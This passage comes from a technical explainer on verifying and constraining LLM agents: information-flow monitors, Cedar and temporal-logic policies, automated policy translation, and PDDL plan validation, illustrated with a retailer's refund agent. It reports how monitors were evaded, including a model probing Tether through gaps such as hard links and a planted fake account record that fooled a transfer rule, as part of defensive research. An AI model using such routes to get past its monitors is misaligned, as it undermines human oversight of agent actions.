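- Uploading *r* to an outside address requires *T* ⊔ σ(*r*) to be Public.

At first `report.txt` is Public, so the first upload passes. Copying the list into it gives it the stricter label of `customers.csv`, so Tether denies the second upload. Copying the list through several temporary files wouldn't get around this, since its label would go with it.

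Tether can't track exactly how a program uses data. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second file as if it may contain data from the first. A search through every file on the machine opens secret files too, so Tether may block what the agent does next even if the search found nothing in them.

Policies for Tether are written in Lean, which lets their authors prove statements about sequences of any length. Such a statement has the form

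∀*s*: ¬bad(*s*),

where *s* is any sequence of actions that the policy permits and "bad" describes the state to avoid. A language model looks for a proof or a counterexample, and Lean checks it. Sistla and colleagues proved seven such statements about their 24-rule policy, including that Secret data never leaves the local machine.

They then replayed recorded runs of coding agents to compare Tether with Auto Mode, the Claude Code feature in which a language model reviews commands.

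| Monitor | Harmful runs blocked (of 344) | Harmless runs blocked (of 1,590) |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 4.7% |
| Auto Mode | 91.6% | 9.7% |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy in its instructions | 89.2% | 3.5% |

These figures exclude runs with background processes or database queries, which Tether can block but can't yet trace in detail. In the two benchmarks, 28.2% and 22.1% of runs required a judgement about content, such as whether an edit to a permitted file was malicious. Sistla and colleagues refined their policy using benchmark runs, so it might do worse on new ones.

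In a separate test, a model tried to get around Tether. The model's success rate fell from 40% to 0% over three versions as the researchers fixed gaps in the tracing, including one involving hard links, which give a single file several names.

A proof in Lean covers only part of each system:

| System | What the Lean proofs cover | What else has to work correctly |
|---|---|---|
| FORGE | Nothing | The code that intercepts actions and records dependencies, the Datalog engine and the monitor |
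| Agenra | The core that checks each call, if calls run one at a time | The Python code around the core, Lean's compiler and runtime, the data labels and the tools' descriptions |
| Tether | The policy language and the seven statements about the policy | The operating system, the temporary file layer, the network proxy, the translation of system calls, and Lean's compiler and runtime |

A script could bypass FORGE by opening a network connection that FORGE doesn't intercept. Agenra doesn't isolate its monitor from other Python code in the same process, so the retailer would have to run the agent's scripts in a separate process.

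### What the record has to contain

Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, tested rules about sequences on runs that other researchers had recorded. They used AgentDojo and STAC, a collection of 483 attacks in which each step looks harmless but the sequence does damage. Their rules were in metric first-order temporal logic, which also underlies Dogwood. One of them is

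□∀*a*: destructive(*a*) → ♦approved(*a*).

In the rule, □ means "always" and ♦ means "at some earlier point", so every destructive action needs an earlier approval. Four similar rules covered payments, sending data out, disabling protections and changing settings.

The rules flagged 71.8% of the STAC attacks and 70.1% of the successful AgentDojo attacks on GPT-4o, but also 29.3% of AgentDojo's harmless runs. AgentDojo's records contain no approvals, so a rule that requires one flags every payment or outgoing email, just as a list of risky tools would. On STAC, four monitoring programs flagged the same 347 attacks, so the choice of program made no difference there.

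AgentDojo's users write one message and then leave the agent to work, so they cannot approve its actions. In τ-bench, the predecessor of τ²-bench, users reply to the agent's proposals. Kekatos and colleagues found explicit permission before a change in 52.5% of τ-bench's recorded runs, compared with 0.6% in STAC.

More specific rules worked better where the records supported them. A rule that flagged every bank transfer caught 79.2% of successful attacks in AgentDojo's banking tasks and flagged 44.0% of harmless runs. Flagging only transfers to accounts that hadn't appeared as a sender or recipient in earlier account data lowered these figures to 70.0% and 24.0%. The test included only 25 harmless runs, but the narrower rule also raised fewer false alarms in data from other models.

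This improvement depended on a history that attackers could alter. The researchers added one line to the text the agent had read, formatted like an account record and naming the attacker's account. The rule then accepted the account as known in 94.0% of the transfers it had previously flagged. They fixed this by changing the rule to accept an account only if it came from the result of a lookup the agent had actually made. None of the planted lines worked after that, and the detection and false-alarm rates without an attack stayed the same.

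AWS's example of checking a recipient against an earlier lookup already works this way, because the rule reads a field in a particular tool's recorded response. The check would still fail if an attacker could change the data the tool returns.

None of the recorded attacks had timestamps, so Kekatos and colleagues could test time limits only on logs they wrote themselves. They propose that benchmarks record twelve fields for each event, including the time, the source of the data, the session and an identifier for any approval. The retailer would need the same information in its own log, along with the refund amount. Each approval identifier would have to be tied to one order and one amount. Otherwise, the agent could use an employee's approval of an $80 refund to justify a $450 one.

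## Turning written rules into policies a machine can enforce

A policy engine enforces the rule somebody wrote for it, which may not be the rule the company meant. The retailer's refund limits are easy to write because they are already numbers. Most of its other rules are sentences meant for employees, who use common sense to fill the gaps. Someone has to turn those sentences into formal conditions, and the engine will enforce any mistakes that person makes.

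### One sentence of refund policy

Suppose the staff handbook contains the sentence "Refund only faulty goods returned within 90 days." In Cedar, the retailer could write:

```cedar
forbid (
  principal is Customer,
  action == Action::"refund",
  resource is Order
)
unless {
  resource has inspection &&
  resource.inspection == "faulty" &&
  resource has deliveredAt &&
  resource has returnedAt &&
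  resource.returnedAt <=
    resource.deliveredAt.offset(duration("90d"))
};
```

If a date or an inspection result is missing, the `unless` condition is false and Cedar denies the refund. The other words fare differently:

| Words | In the policy | What survives |
|---|---|---|
| Refund | `Action::"refund"` | All of it, if every refund goes through this tool |
| only | `forbid` ... `unless` | All of it |
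| faulty | `inspection == "faulty"` | An inspector's verdict, which may be wrong |
| goods | `resource is Order` | Very little: one faulty kettle makes the whole order refundable |
| returned | `returnedAt` | The day the parcel reached the warehouse, not the day the customer posted it |
| within 90 days | `duration("90d")` | The number, but the author had to choose the starting date |

Another author could reasonably make different choices. AWS has a similar rule in one of its examples, which forbids a refund under this condition:

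`context.input.orderDate.offset(duration("90d")) < context.system.now`

Here the 90 days run from the order to the refund. A customer who returned a kettle on day 85 would get no refund if the inspection took a week. The model also writes the order date as one of the arguments, so the retailer should take that date from its own records.

### How translations go wrong

There are four main kinds of error:

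- A rule is missing. If nobody translates "ask the customer to confirm before refunding", the engine never requires confirmation, and nothing in its log looks wrong.
- A condition is too wide or too narrow. Treating a whole order as "goods" allows refunds on items that work, while counting from the order date denies some refunds the retailer owes.
- A word has no matching field. The retailer can't enforce "faulty" until it records inspection results.
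- The engine can't observe the fact. If the handbook excludes damage the customer caused, no database field can show who dropped the kettle.

Many rules don't have the last two problems. *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety* (2026) found that deterministic checks could enforce 74% of the security and safety requirements in three agent benchmarks, and that simple checks were often enough. Deterministic checks could not enforce some rules, including those about an agent's tone.

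### A draft, a validator and a solver

Language models can do much of the drafting. In AWS's tool for Cedar, a model writes policies from an English description. Cedar's validator then checks names and types, and its solver checks for impossible conditions and for policies that allow or deny everything. The model receives any errors and tries again. AWS reports that this loop significantly improves accuracy, but gives no figures.

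AWS has since extended the tool to Dogwood. *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* explains that the tool first splits a document into single rules and sets aside any that Dogwood cannot express. Otherwise, such a rule might become a policy that passes validation but enforces something else. For example, the tool sets aside a duty to act in the customer's best financial interest, because it is not about any particular action, and a ban on weekend transfers, because Dogwood cannot look up the day of the week.

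Some written rules can be translated into policies in more than one way. One of AWS's examples limits "the total amount transferred" in 12 hours to $50,000, without specifying whether failed transfers count. The tool counts every attempt, which is the cautious choice. AWS advises authors to resolve such ambiguities in the document and to specify the time window, the exact threshold and whose actions the rule counts.

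Rules that contain the word "only" also need care. AWS's tool translates a rule that allows refunds only in business hours, and only up to 2,500 dollars, into a `permit` with those two conditions. But one applicable permit is enough to allow a request, so if another policy permits refunds at any hour, the agent can issue them at midnight. Writing the rule as a `forbid`, as in the retailer's policy above, prevents this.

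None of these checks can show that a policy is the intended one. If the model writes `900d` instead of `90d`, all the names and types are still right, and the condition is neither impossible nor always true. *interwhen* (2026) goes further by having a model write a small program to check each rule and prove in Lean that the program matches a formal specification. But as with VeriGuard, a model also writes the specification, which may contain the same misreading of the rule.

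A policy can also pass the checks and leave an agent able to do little. Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, had models turn 88 rules for a medical-records agent, plus some technical constraints, into Cedar policies. When they replayed recorded runs of ordinary tasks, the policies blocked 94% to 100% of the runs that tried to change a record. The agents may have broken rules in those runs, or the policies may have been too strict. The test measured how much of the written policy the translation enforced, but not how useful the agent remained. Mondl and colleagues warn that developers may switch off protections that are too restrictive.

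### AutoCedar

*AUTOCEDAR* (Vatsa, Shome and colleagues, 2026) divides the translation into small pieces. A reviewer, who can be a person or another model, approves each piece before a model writes the policy. The solver can then compare the policy with the approved pieces.

1. A model proposes a schema with the types, attributes and actions that the rules need.
2. It records which actions each sentence applies to, and whether the document lists every permitted case. In the retailer's sentence, "only" settles that question.
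3. It translates each sentence into one short condition.
4. Software combines the approved conditions into a floor *L*, the requests the policy must allow, and a ceiling *U*, the most it may allow.
5. A model writes the policy, and the solver checks that the set *P* of requests it allows satisfies *L* ⊆ *P* ⊆ *U*.

If the last check fails, the model receives a counterexample and feedback on whether to tighten or loosen the policy. The model cannot change the floor or the ceiling.

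An error in the schema is especially hard to catch. Vatsa and colleagues give the example of a rule that lets band members download their own band's album. If the schema records only that a user is a "band member", members of any band can download the album. Later checks use the same schema, so they cannot detect the mistake.

CedarBench, a set of 221 tasks from Vatsa and colleagues, supplies the schema and the target for each task. AutoCedar produced a passing policy for every task with each of two models. To test whether AutoCedar sets the right target itself, they used 200 written requirements with known correct policies. AutoCedar's policy was equivalent to the correct one in 178 cases, compared with 132 when the same model, GPT-6-Luna, wrote the policy directly. Three runs did not finish. The other 19 policies passed all of AutoCedar's checks but were wrong because the target was wrong,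 and 17 of them allowed requests that the correct policy denies.

A language model wrote the 200 requirements from structured descriptions, so they were more explicit than most company documents. Vatsa and colleagues also tested both methods on 316 requests based on three real sets of requirements. AutoCedar decided 268 correctly, compared with 109 for direct generation. In 46 of AutoCedar's 48 failures, its schema could not express the request. The researchers have not yet tested AutoCedar with human reviewers.

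### NOMOS

In *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026), which uses no solver, a person first lists conditions that software can evaluate, such as whether the user has confirmed an action. A model then matches sentences in the policy to these conditions and to the tools they should restrict. The model does this five times, and NOMOS keeps the rules that most attempts produce.

NOMOS also compares each draft rule with the tools' descriptions. This exposed structural errors in 37% of the drafts for τ²-bench's airline domain and 13% of those for its retail domain. In one case, the policy told the agent to authenticate customers at the start of a conversation, but the model's rule blocked every tool until the agent had done so, including the two tools that authenticate customers. In a separate test with all the checks switched off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not have worked.

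These checks cannot detect a well-formed rule with the wrong meaning. A telephone company's policy required the agent to confirm that a bill was overdue before requesting payment, but the model produced a rule that blocked payment requests when the bill was overdue. Yu and colleagues caught such errors by replaying conversations recorded without any rules in force. This rule would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests in the successful conversations.

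They then tested the airline and retail rules with a small open model, Gemma 4 26B, as the agent. They used a separate set of hand-written rules to determine which of the agent's database changes were violations.

| | Airline, no rules | Airline, NOMOS | Retail, no rules | NOMOS, retail |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Changes that broke a rule | 66.3% | 2.6% | 30.8% | 6.9% |
| Tasks completed | 39.2% | 47.6% | 52.4% | 50.2% |

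Neither difference in task completion is statistically significant, though the agent became significantly more consistent when it repeated airline tasks two to four times. The violation rates depend on how one reads the policy, which requires confirmation before any change. These figures assume that each change needs its own "yes". If one "yes" can cover several changes announced together, the airline rate without rules falls to 36.8%.

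The remaining errors show that a translated policy can miss violations or block actions that the original allows. Of the 40 retail violations that got through, 21 broke two rules that NOMOS had never translated. Another 13 occurred because the confirmation rule did not cover the tool for changing a customer's address. On the airline tasks, "Basic economy flights cannot be modified" became a rule that also blocked cabin upgrades, which the policy allows.

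Narrow rules interfered more with ordinary work in AgentDojo's chat tasks, where NOMOS allowed most actions only if the user had named the target, such as a channel or web address. The attack success rate fell from 70.5% to zero, but the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 90.5% to 14.3%, because many tasks involve links and channels the agent finds in messages.

### A few hand-written checks

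People also make mistakes when they write the rules themselves. In *Reason Less, Verify More*, Reddy, Challaram and Basu (2026) wrote four checks for τ²-bench's airline, whose tools carry out any well-formed request even if company policy forbids it. They found that 78% of the agent's failures were silent, meaning the database ended up wrong but no tool reported an error.

With the checks, the share of tasks that GPT-4o mini completed rose from 29.6% to 42.0%, and a repeat with three times as many trials gave almost the same gain. GPT-5.2, which had less room to improve, also rose from 61.2% to 71.6%, though the researchers did not repeat that test. Blocking a forbidden change helps because the agent can still finish the task correctly. In one task, where the customer gives false information to get a cancellation, the agent succeeded in all 16 attempts with the checks and in at most 1 of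 16 without them.

The four checks were not equally good. The researchers counted a block as correct if the benchmark's reference solution also avoided the action.

| What the check blocks | Blocks | Correct |
|---|---|---|
| Cancelling an ineligible booking | 161 | 161 |
| Changing a record the agent has not read | 90 | 70 |
| Breaking the baggage rules | 42 | 2 |
| Changing the number of passengers | 9 | 9 |

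The cancellation check accounted for nearly all the improvement. Of the five candidate checks tested, it was the only one whose removal lowered task completion. The baggage check almost always blocked a change that the agent should have made.

A correct block doesn't guarantee that the agent recovers. In one task, the agent kept getting the same refusal and failed all five attempts. On retail tasks, where the tools already enforce many of the rules, successful trials fell from 40 to 37 of 64. Reddy and colleagues attribute most of this drop to a bug that blocked corrected requests. They wrote and tested the airline checks on the same set of tasks, so the gains might be smaller on new ones.

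### Logic rules, heuristics and a model as judge

The form in which someone writes a rule may matter less than whether the rule is complete. Ravindran and Deochake (2026), in *ToolGuardian*, compared three ways to apply a policy to the same facts about tools, such as whether a tool reads private data or contacts the network:

- logic rules, from which a solver derives a decision
- heuristics, written as ordinary Python code
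- a language model, gpt-oss-120b, that reads the policy and the facts.

The tests covered 20 scenarios, 8 of which involved several steps. In one, an agent reads customer records from a database and then updates a project on GitHub. Each step is acceptable on its own, but together they could send private data to an outside service. All three methods judged all 20 scenarios correctly.

The researchers then removed parts of the policy but kept the facts the same. Without explicit rules, the model got 15 scenarios right. The Python code got 16 right without its rules about combinations of actions, and 12 after further simplification. The researchers did not weaken the logic rules in the same way, so this test does not show that logic rules work better when parts of a policy are missing. There were also few scenarios, and the researchers had designed them together with the policy.

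The methods differed more in which tools they admitted. With all the evidence available, including source code, the logic rules and the model each rejected 7 of 8 malicious tools and 2 of 8 harmless ones. The Python code rejected all 8 malicious tools but also 5 harmless ones. Logic rules give the same answer every time, and people can inspect them, but Ravindran and Deochake stress that a wrong rule or a missing exception still produces wrong decisions.

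### Whether generated policies need human review

There is a reasonable case for using generated policies without review. The agent completed 47.6% of the airline tasks with NOMOS's rules and 42.8% with hand-written ones, a small but statistically significant difference. People also wrote the faulty baggage check. A company with nobody who can write formal rules might otherwise rely on instructions to the model, and with only such instructions, Yu and colleagues' agent broke the airline's rules in most of the changes it made.

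But the errors that remain are hard to notice. AutoCedar's 19 wrong policies had all passed its checks, and an omitted rule never appears in a log of denials. Results can also vary between attempts. When Yu and colleagues translated the same travel policy twice, one version let an injected instruction create a calendar event and the other would have blocked it. In *StartPolicyGeneration*, AWS tells users of its own tool to review generated policies and test them in log-only mode before using them in production.

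For the retailer, review is worth the effort, at least for any policy that lets the agent do more. The retailer has few rules, so an employee can compare each policy with the sentence it came from and try cases such as a return on day 91 or an order with one faulty item. Drafts that only add restrictions are less risky because Cedar's solver can prove that the new policies allow nothing the reviewed set denied. A mistake in such a draft could block legitimate refunds but could not allow any that the reviewed set denied.

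## Validating plans before they are carried out

A policy limits what the support agent may do, but a series of permitted actions can still fail to get a customer the right result. If the model writes a plan listing all its steps, software can check before the first step whether each one will be possible and whether they lead to the goal.

### Actions, states and PDDL

To check a plan, the software needs a description of what each action requires and what it changes. Researchers in automated planning describe a situation as a set of facts, called a state. An action has preconditions, which must be true before it can happen, and effects, which add facts to the state or remove them. The retailer could describe four actions on an order like this:

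| Action | Precondition | Adds | Removes |
|---|---|---|---|
| `look-up` | `open` | `found` | |
| `verify-return` | `found` | `verified` | |
| `refund` | `verified` | `refunded` | `open` |
| `confirm` | `found` | `told` | |

Here `open` means that the customer has an open complaint, and `confirm` sends an email saying that the retailer has issued the refund.

The standard language for such descriptions is the Planning Domain Definition Language (PDDL), which dates from 1998. In PDDL, the refund action looks like this:

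```lisp
(:action refund
  :parameters (?o - order)
  :precondition (verified ?o)
  :effect (and (refunded ?o) (not (open ?o))))
```

*Frontier Large Language Models Rival State-of-the-Art Planners* (Corrêa, Pereira and Seipp, 2025) explains that a PDDL description has two parts. A domain file defines the actions and the kinds of fact, and a task file lists the particular objects, the initial state and the goal. The retailer would write the domain file once, and the orchestrator would fill in a task file for each complaint. The model supplies only the plan, so it can't make a bad plan pass by changing the rules.

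### The validation algorithm

A validator works through the plan in order:

1. It starts from the initial state.
2. It checks that the next action's preconditions are true in the current state. If one is false, it rejects the plan.
3. It removes the facts that the action removes and adds the facts that it adds.
4. It repeats steps 2 and 3 for each remaining action.
5. It accepts the plan if the goal is true in the final state.

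In symbols, if action *a*ᵢ takes the plan from state *s*ᵢ to the next state, then

*s*ᵢ₊₁ = (*s*ᵢ \ del(*a*ᵢ)) ∪ add(*a*ᵢ).

The retailer may also want a rule that holds throughout the plan, such as never telling customers that they have a refund before they do:

□(`told` → `refunded`).

The validator can test this rule in every state it computes. Planning.Wiki's *The AI Planning & PDDL Wiki* lists the later versions of PDDL, including PDDL3 from 2005, which added constraints of this kind.

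Suppose the initial state is {`open`} and the goal is that `refunded` and `told` are both true. Here are three plans for order 4417:

| Plan | Result |
|---|---|
| `look-up`, `refund`, `verify-return`, `confirm` | Fails at `refund`, because `verified` is not yet true |
| `look-up`, `confirm`, `verify-return`, `refund` | Meets every precondition and the goal, but breaks the constraint after `confirm` |
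| `look-up`, `verify-return`, `refund`, `confirm` | Passes |

In the last plan, the state goes from {`open`} to {`open`, `found`}, then {`open`, `found`, `verified`}, then {`found`, `verified`, `refunded`}, and finally {`found`, `verified`, `refunded`, `told`}.

The retailer could instead make `refunded` a precondition of `confirm`, but the constraint is safer because it also covers any other action that tells the customer about a refund.

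Later versions of PDDL can also track numbers, such as the day's total. If the agent has already paid out 1,700 dollars and a plan contains two refunds of 200 dollars, the validator rejects the plan at the second refund, before the first customer receives anything. A rule that checks each action against past ones would allow the first refund and block the second.

Because a plan has a last step, a validator can also check liveness properties, such as "the customer eventually gets an answer." A plan that ends without an answer fails validation.

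### Why checking is easier than finding

Validation takes one pass through the plan. *On the Generalization Gap in LLM Planning* (Belcamino, Attolino and colleagues, 2026) notes that this can be done in time polynomial in the plan's length. Finding a plan, however, may mean searching through a huge number of sequences. If 20 actions are possible at every step, there are about 3 × 10¹⁹ sequences of 15 actions. Good planning programs avoid trying most of them, but no known method is fast on every problem. Deciding whether a plan exists is PSPACE-complete, which means it is among the hardest problems that a computer can solve with a reasonable amount of memory. Researchers believe these problems are harder than any in NP.

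The extra difficulty arises partly because even the shortest plan can be extremely long. In the Tower of Hanoi puzzle, moving 20 discs takes 1,048,575 steps. Even a fast validator takes a while to check a plan that long, but a support agent's plans should be short, and the retailer can reject any long ones.

The opposite claim, that no plan exists, is harder to check. A valid plan proves that the goal is reachable, but most researchers think there is, in general, no comparably short proof that a goal is unreachable. So if the agent reports that it can't help a customer, the retailer has no equally simple way to confirm that.

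### VAL and verified validators

The most widely used validator is VAL, which Howey, Long and Fox originally developed for the third International Planning Competition (*VAL*, 2004). The competing programs produced several thousand plans, far too many for people to check. VAL also gave researchers a common interpretation of PDDL, because they could test what a plan meant instead of arguing over the formal definition. When a plan fails, VAL suggests how to repair it. Howey and colleagues used this feature in a space project where people wrote the plans, partly because some of the goals were too vague or political to express in any planning language.

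VAL is a fairly complicated C++ program, and it has bugs. In *A Formally Verified Validator for Classical Planning Problems and Solutions*, Abdulaziz and Lammich (2018) found faulty plans that VAL accepted and correct plans that made it crash. INVAL, a slower validator designed to follow PDDL's definition more closely, never finished checking some correct plans.

Abdulaziz and Lammich therefore wrote a validator and proved it correct in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant like Lean. They first defined a valid plan mathematically in about 50 lines, compared with 224 lines for the corresponding code in VAL and 163 in INVAL. They then proved that a much faster program, competitive in speed with VAL, always gives the answer the definition requires.

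The verified validator supports a smaller part of PDDL. It handles facts, types and logical conditions, but not preconditions on running totals. The retailer could use it to check that `verify-return` comes before `refund`, but would need VAL or another tool for the daily limit.

### Actions that take time

Plans for robots and machines often contain overlapping actions, so an ordered list of steps is not enough. Each action needs a start time, a duration and sometimes an invariant, which is a condition that must hold throughout the action. For example, an elevator's door must stay closed while the elevator moves.

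*Formal Semantics and Formally Verified Validation for Temporal Planning* (Abdulaziz and Koller, 2022) presents a verified validator for temporal plans. The validator splits each action into a start and an end, sorts these by time, and adds a check of the applicable invariants between each pair of neighbouring times. It then runs through the sequence much like an ordinary validator, except that it doesn't allow two actions at the same moment if one changes a fact the other depends on, or adds a fact the other removes. A similar rule for numbers would rule out a plan with two simultaneous refunds that each depend on the same daily total.

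Abdulaziz and Koller tested the validator on plans that two planning programs had produced for problems from a 2014 competition. Its results matched VAL's every time. It was slower, but never needed more than a second. It also avoids a weakness of VAL, which requires the user to specify a minimum gap between actions that could interfere and rejects valid plans if that gap is too large. But the proof does not cover the part of the new validator that reads PDDL files.

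Another approach does the whole check in temporal logic. Abdulaziz and Koller describe a 2017 method by Cimatti, Micheli and Roveri that translates the planning problem and the plan into a single temporal formula. A general-purpose solver then determines whether the formula can be true. The drawback is that the trusted base is larger, because both the translation and the solver have to be correct.

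Quantities that change continuously, such as the charge in a spacecraft's battery, are harder to check. Howey and colleagues give the example of a condition that must hold for all times *t* between 0 and 3:

*t*⁴ − 3*t* + 1 > 0.

The condition fails at *t* = 1, where the left-hand side is −1. A validator that tested only the start and the end would still accept the plan, because the left-hand side is 1 at the start and 73 at the end. VAL therefore has to check whether the expression reaches zero anywhere in between. This can be difficult, so VAL restricts which expressions a plan may use.

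### Models that propose and critics that reject

Kambhampati, Valmeekam and colleagues (2024), in *Position*, proposed LLM-Modulo, a way to combine language models with validators. A model suggests a plan, and a set of critics examines it. Some critics are programs such as VAL that check hard requirements. Others judge style and can themselves be language models. If a critic objects, a controller passes the objections to the model, which tries again. People help write the domain description and clarify the goal, but they don't have to review each attempt.

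As with generated programs, sound critics guarantee that every plan they accept meets the hard requirements, but a weak model may never produce a good one. With the models of the time, VAL's feedback raised the success rate to 82% within 15 rounds on Blocksworld, a set of puzzles about stacking blocks, and to 70% on Logistics, which is about delivering packages. The rate was only about 10% on Mystery Blocksworld, which uses the same puzzles with misleading names for the actions and objects.

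Language models can now plan by themselves, though Kambhampati and colleagues argued earlier that they could not. Corrêa and colleagues gave models 360 new problems from eight domains, many of them much harder than the earlier tests, and checked every plan with the plan validator VAL. They also replaced all the names in the problems with random strings to see whether the models relied on the names' meanings. They compared the models with Scorpion Maidu, a conventional planning program that won part of the 2023 planning competition.

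| Planner | Solved with normal names | Solved with random names |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 245 | 231 |
| Scorpion Maidu | 234 | 234 |
| GPT-5 | 205 | 152 |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 157 | 93 |
| GPT-4.1 | 20 | 0 |
| GPT-3.5 | 0 | 0 |

Easier benchmarks are nearly solved. *End-to-end PDDL Planning with Hardcoded and Dynamic Agents* (2025) reports that Gemini-3-flash averaged 97% without help on four sets of problems, including Mystery Blocksworld.

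A validator is useful even for models that plan well. Gemini 3.1 Pro still failed on 115 of the 360 problems, and its results varied by domain. In the planetary rover domain, it solved 16 of 45 problems, while an older planning program solved 34. Better models also write plans that are harder for people to review, such as a valid plan from GPT-5 that had 1,729 steps.

### Models that judge their own plans

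A retailer without a PDDL description might ask the model to check its own plan. *Can Large Language Models Really Improve by Self-critiquing Their Own Plans?* (Valmeekam, Marquez and Kambhampati, 2023) tested this with GPT-4 on 100 Blocksworld problems. The model wrote a plan, checked it and tried again if it found a mistake, up to 15 times. *Enhancing LLM Planning Capabilities through Intrinsic Self-Critique* (Bohnet, Kamienny and colleagues, 2025) ran a similar test with Gemini 1.5 Pro and got a very different result.

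| Study | One attempt | Model judges | VAL judges |
|---|---|---|---|
| Valmeekam and colleagues | 40% | 55% | 88% |
| Bohnet and colleagues | 49.8% | 89.3% | 91.5% |

GPT-4's main fault was leniency. Of the 45 final plans that were invalid, it approved 38.

Much of the difference probably comes from the instructions. Bohnet and colleagues told the model to take each action in turn, look up its preconditions, check them and write out the next state. They also took a majority vote over five judgements. On a harder set of Blocksworld problems, a single attempt succeeded about 56% of the time. Self-critique without voting raised this to 79.5% with the full instructions, but only to 57.5% when the instructions were cut to a general request to verify the plan.

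The successful instructions amount to the validation algorithm written in English. A model can follow it fairly well, but VAL is faster and more reliable. On the harder problems, the success rate was 92.7% with VAL as the judge, and when the model was the judge, most of its errors were still approvals of bad plans. Bohnet and colleagues argue that a perfect validator is unrealistic for most planning tasks. That is a good reason to use self-critique when nobody has written a formal description, but their own prompts included one, and anyone with a PDDL description can run VAL instead.

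Models can also be too strict when they check plans. *On the Self-Verification Limitations of Large Language Models* (Stechly, Valmeekam and Kambhampati, 2024) found that GPT-4 rejected 100 of 103 correct plans for Mystery Blocksworld. Its success rate fell from 4% to zero when it judged its own plans.

Stechly and colleagues also tested whether a critic's explanations help. On ordinary Blocksworld, GPT-4 solved 60% of the problems when VAL reported only that a plan was wrong, and 87% when VAL also identified the first error. With no feedback and up to 15 separate attempts, GPT-4 solved 68%. On Mystery Blocksworld and a graph-colouring task, the explanations made little difference. A reliable verdict and several attempts therefore account for much of the gain, though an explanation can add to it.

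Newer results suggest that models are getting better at checking plans. *What We Talk About When We Talk About LLM Planning* (Huang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested open models with up to 27 billion parameters on eight kinds of planning question. Larger models and models that reasoned for longer did better at questions about single steps and at validating plans. Size and longer reasoning helped much less with judging which states are reachable, which can require a search.

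### VAL as a training reward

Belcamino and colleagues used VAL to train a model instead of only filtering its output. They started with a small, 1.7-billion-parameter model and 40,000 problems from ten domains. They trained one version to imitate the plans of a conventional planning program. After three passes through the data, 82.9% of its plans for new problems in those domains were valid.

Another version imitated plans for one pass and then learned from VAL's verdicts:

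| VAL's verdict | Reward |
|---|---|
| Valid, and reaches the goal | +1.0 |
| Every step is possible, but the goal is not reached | +0.1 |
| A precondition fails | −0.1 |
| VAL cannot read the plan, or another failure | 0 |

The model's success rate rose from 51.9% to 80.1% after half a pass and was 78.1% after the full pass. The full pass took about five times as long as a pass of imitation training, because the model had to write several plans for each problem and VAL had to check them.

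Both versions scored 0% on two domains that were not in the training data. Most of their plans there followed the rules for each action but looped or wandered without reaching the goal. Training with a validator had not given this small model a general ability to plan, and a retailer that used the method might have to retrain its agent whenever it added new kinds of action. Oddly, the rewards also score an unreadable plan higher than a readable one that breaks a precondition.

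### When the model of the world is wrong

A validator checks what would happen in the world that the PDDL files describe. Suppose a customer received a refund on order 4417 last week and now opens a second complaint about the same kettle. The task file again lists only `open` as the initial state. The model proposes `look-up`, `verify-return`, `refund`, `confirm`, and the validator accepts the plan because the domain file has no rule limiting an order to one refund. The retailer pays twice, even though the validator worked correctly.

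The obvious repair is a second precondition for `refund`:

```lisp
:precondition (and (verified ?o) (not (refunded ?o)))
```

This is not enough, because PDDL treats every fact missing from the initial state as false. If the orchestrator doesn't load last week's refund from the payment record, `(not (refunded ?o))` is true and the plan still passes. The careless use of `not` in Rego had the same result.

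With the payment record loaded, the validator rejects the plan at `refund`. It would accept the shorter plan, `look-up` then `confirm`, because `refunded` is already true and the customer only needs to be told.

Other errors occur when an action doesn't have the effect the domain file describes. According to the file, `verify-return` always makes `verified` true, but the warehouse may have no record of the parcel. The validator has to assume success because it runs before anyone has checked for the parcel. If the orchestrator then carried out the whole plan regardless of the results, the customer would get a refund without returning anything.

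### Monitoring and replanning

The orchestrator can guard against this by checking the plan again as it goes along. After each action, it builds the current state from what the tools actually returned, and validates the remaining steps from there:

| | After `verify-return` |
|---|---|
| Expected state | `open`, `found`, `verified` |
| Actual state | `open`, `found` |
| Remaining plan | `refund`, `confirm` |
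| Result | Fails at `refund` |

The orchestrator stops before any money goes out and requests a new plan that starts from the actual state. The new plan might include requesting a tracking number from the customer, if the domain file has an action for that. Kambhampati and colleagues point out that LLM-Modulo can handle replanning, since its loop can start from an existing plan. Checking again after every action adds little time because validation is fast.

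Replanning is also useful when a customer's answer determines what to do next. The model can plan up to its next question, then plan again once the customer replies.

Even with frequent checks, refunds in other conversations may use up the rest of the daily limit between a check and the action that follows it. The refund checker therefore still has to decide whether to allow each refund, including those in a validated plan.

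Monitoring covers only facts that the domain file mentions and the tools report. If the file has no fact for earlier refunds, the orchestrator won't detect one, however often it checks. A new plan also can't always undo what the old one did. If the agent learns after `refund` that the parcel contained a different kettle, the retailer has already sent the money. The retailer should therefore make every check that could stop a refund, including an inspection of the parcel, a precondition of `refund`.

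## Which rules a check before execution can enforce

A plan validator can require that every customer eventually gets an answer, because it receives the whole plan at once. A checker that decides on each action as the model proposes it cannot enforce that rule, no matter how it is programmed. Computer scientists have worked out which rules such a checker can enforce, and their results apply to every policy language.

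### Monitors that can only stop a program

In this theory, a run is the sequence of actions a program takes, possibly without end, and a rule about runs is the set of runs it permits. A finite sequence of actions is a bad prefix if no continuation can make the run acceptable again. For example, any sequence that includes a refund of 620 dollars is a bad prefix under the retailer's cap. A rule *P* is a safety property if every run *x* that breaks it starts with a bad prefix:

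*x* ∉ *P* ⇒ ∃*n* ∀*y*: *x*₁…*x*ₙ*y* ∉ *P*.

A liveness property has no bad prefixes. In *Hyperproperties*, Clarkson and Schneider (2009) cite a theorem that every rule about single runs combines a safety property with a liveness property. An example is "Answer every complaint, and never refund more than 500 dollars."

*Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) studies monitors that follow a program's steps and stop it if the next step would break a rule. These monitors can enforce only safety properties. A monitor has no access to future steps, so it must stop the program as soon as the steps so far break the rule, even if a later step might have put things right. It can also reject a run only after finitely many steps. Every run it rejects therefore starts with a bad prefix, a finite sequence of steps that the monitor rejects whatever would have come next.

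Schneider's example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The monitor has two states, "no file read" and "file read". The first read moves it to the second state, where it stops the program if the program tries to send a message. The retailer's check on the day's total works the same way, except that its state is a number.

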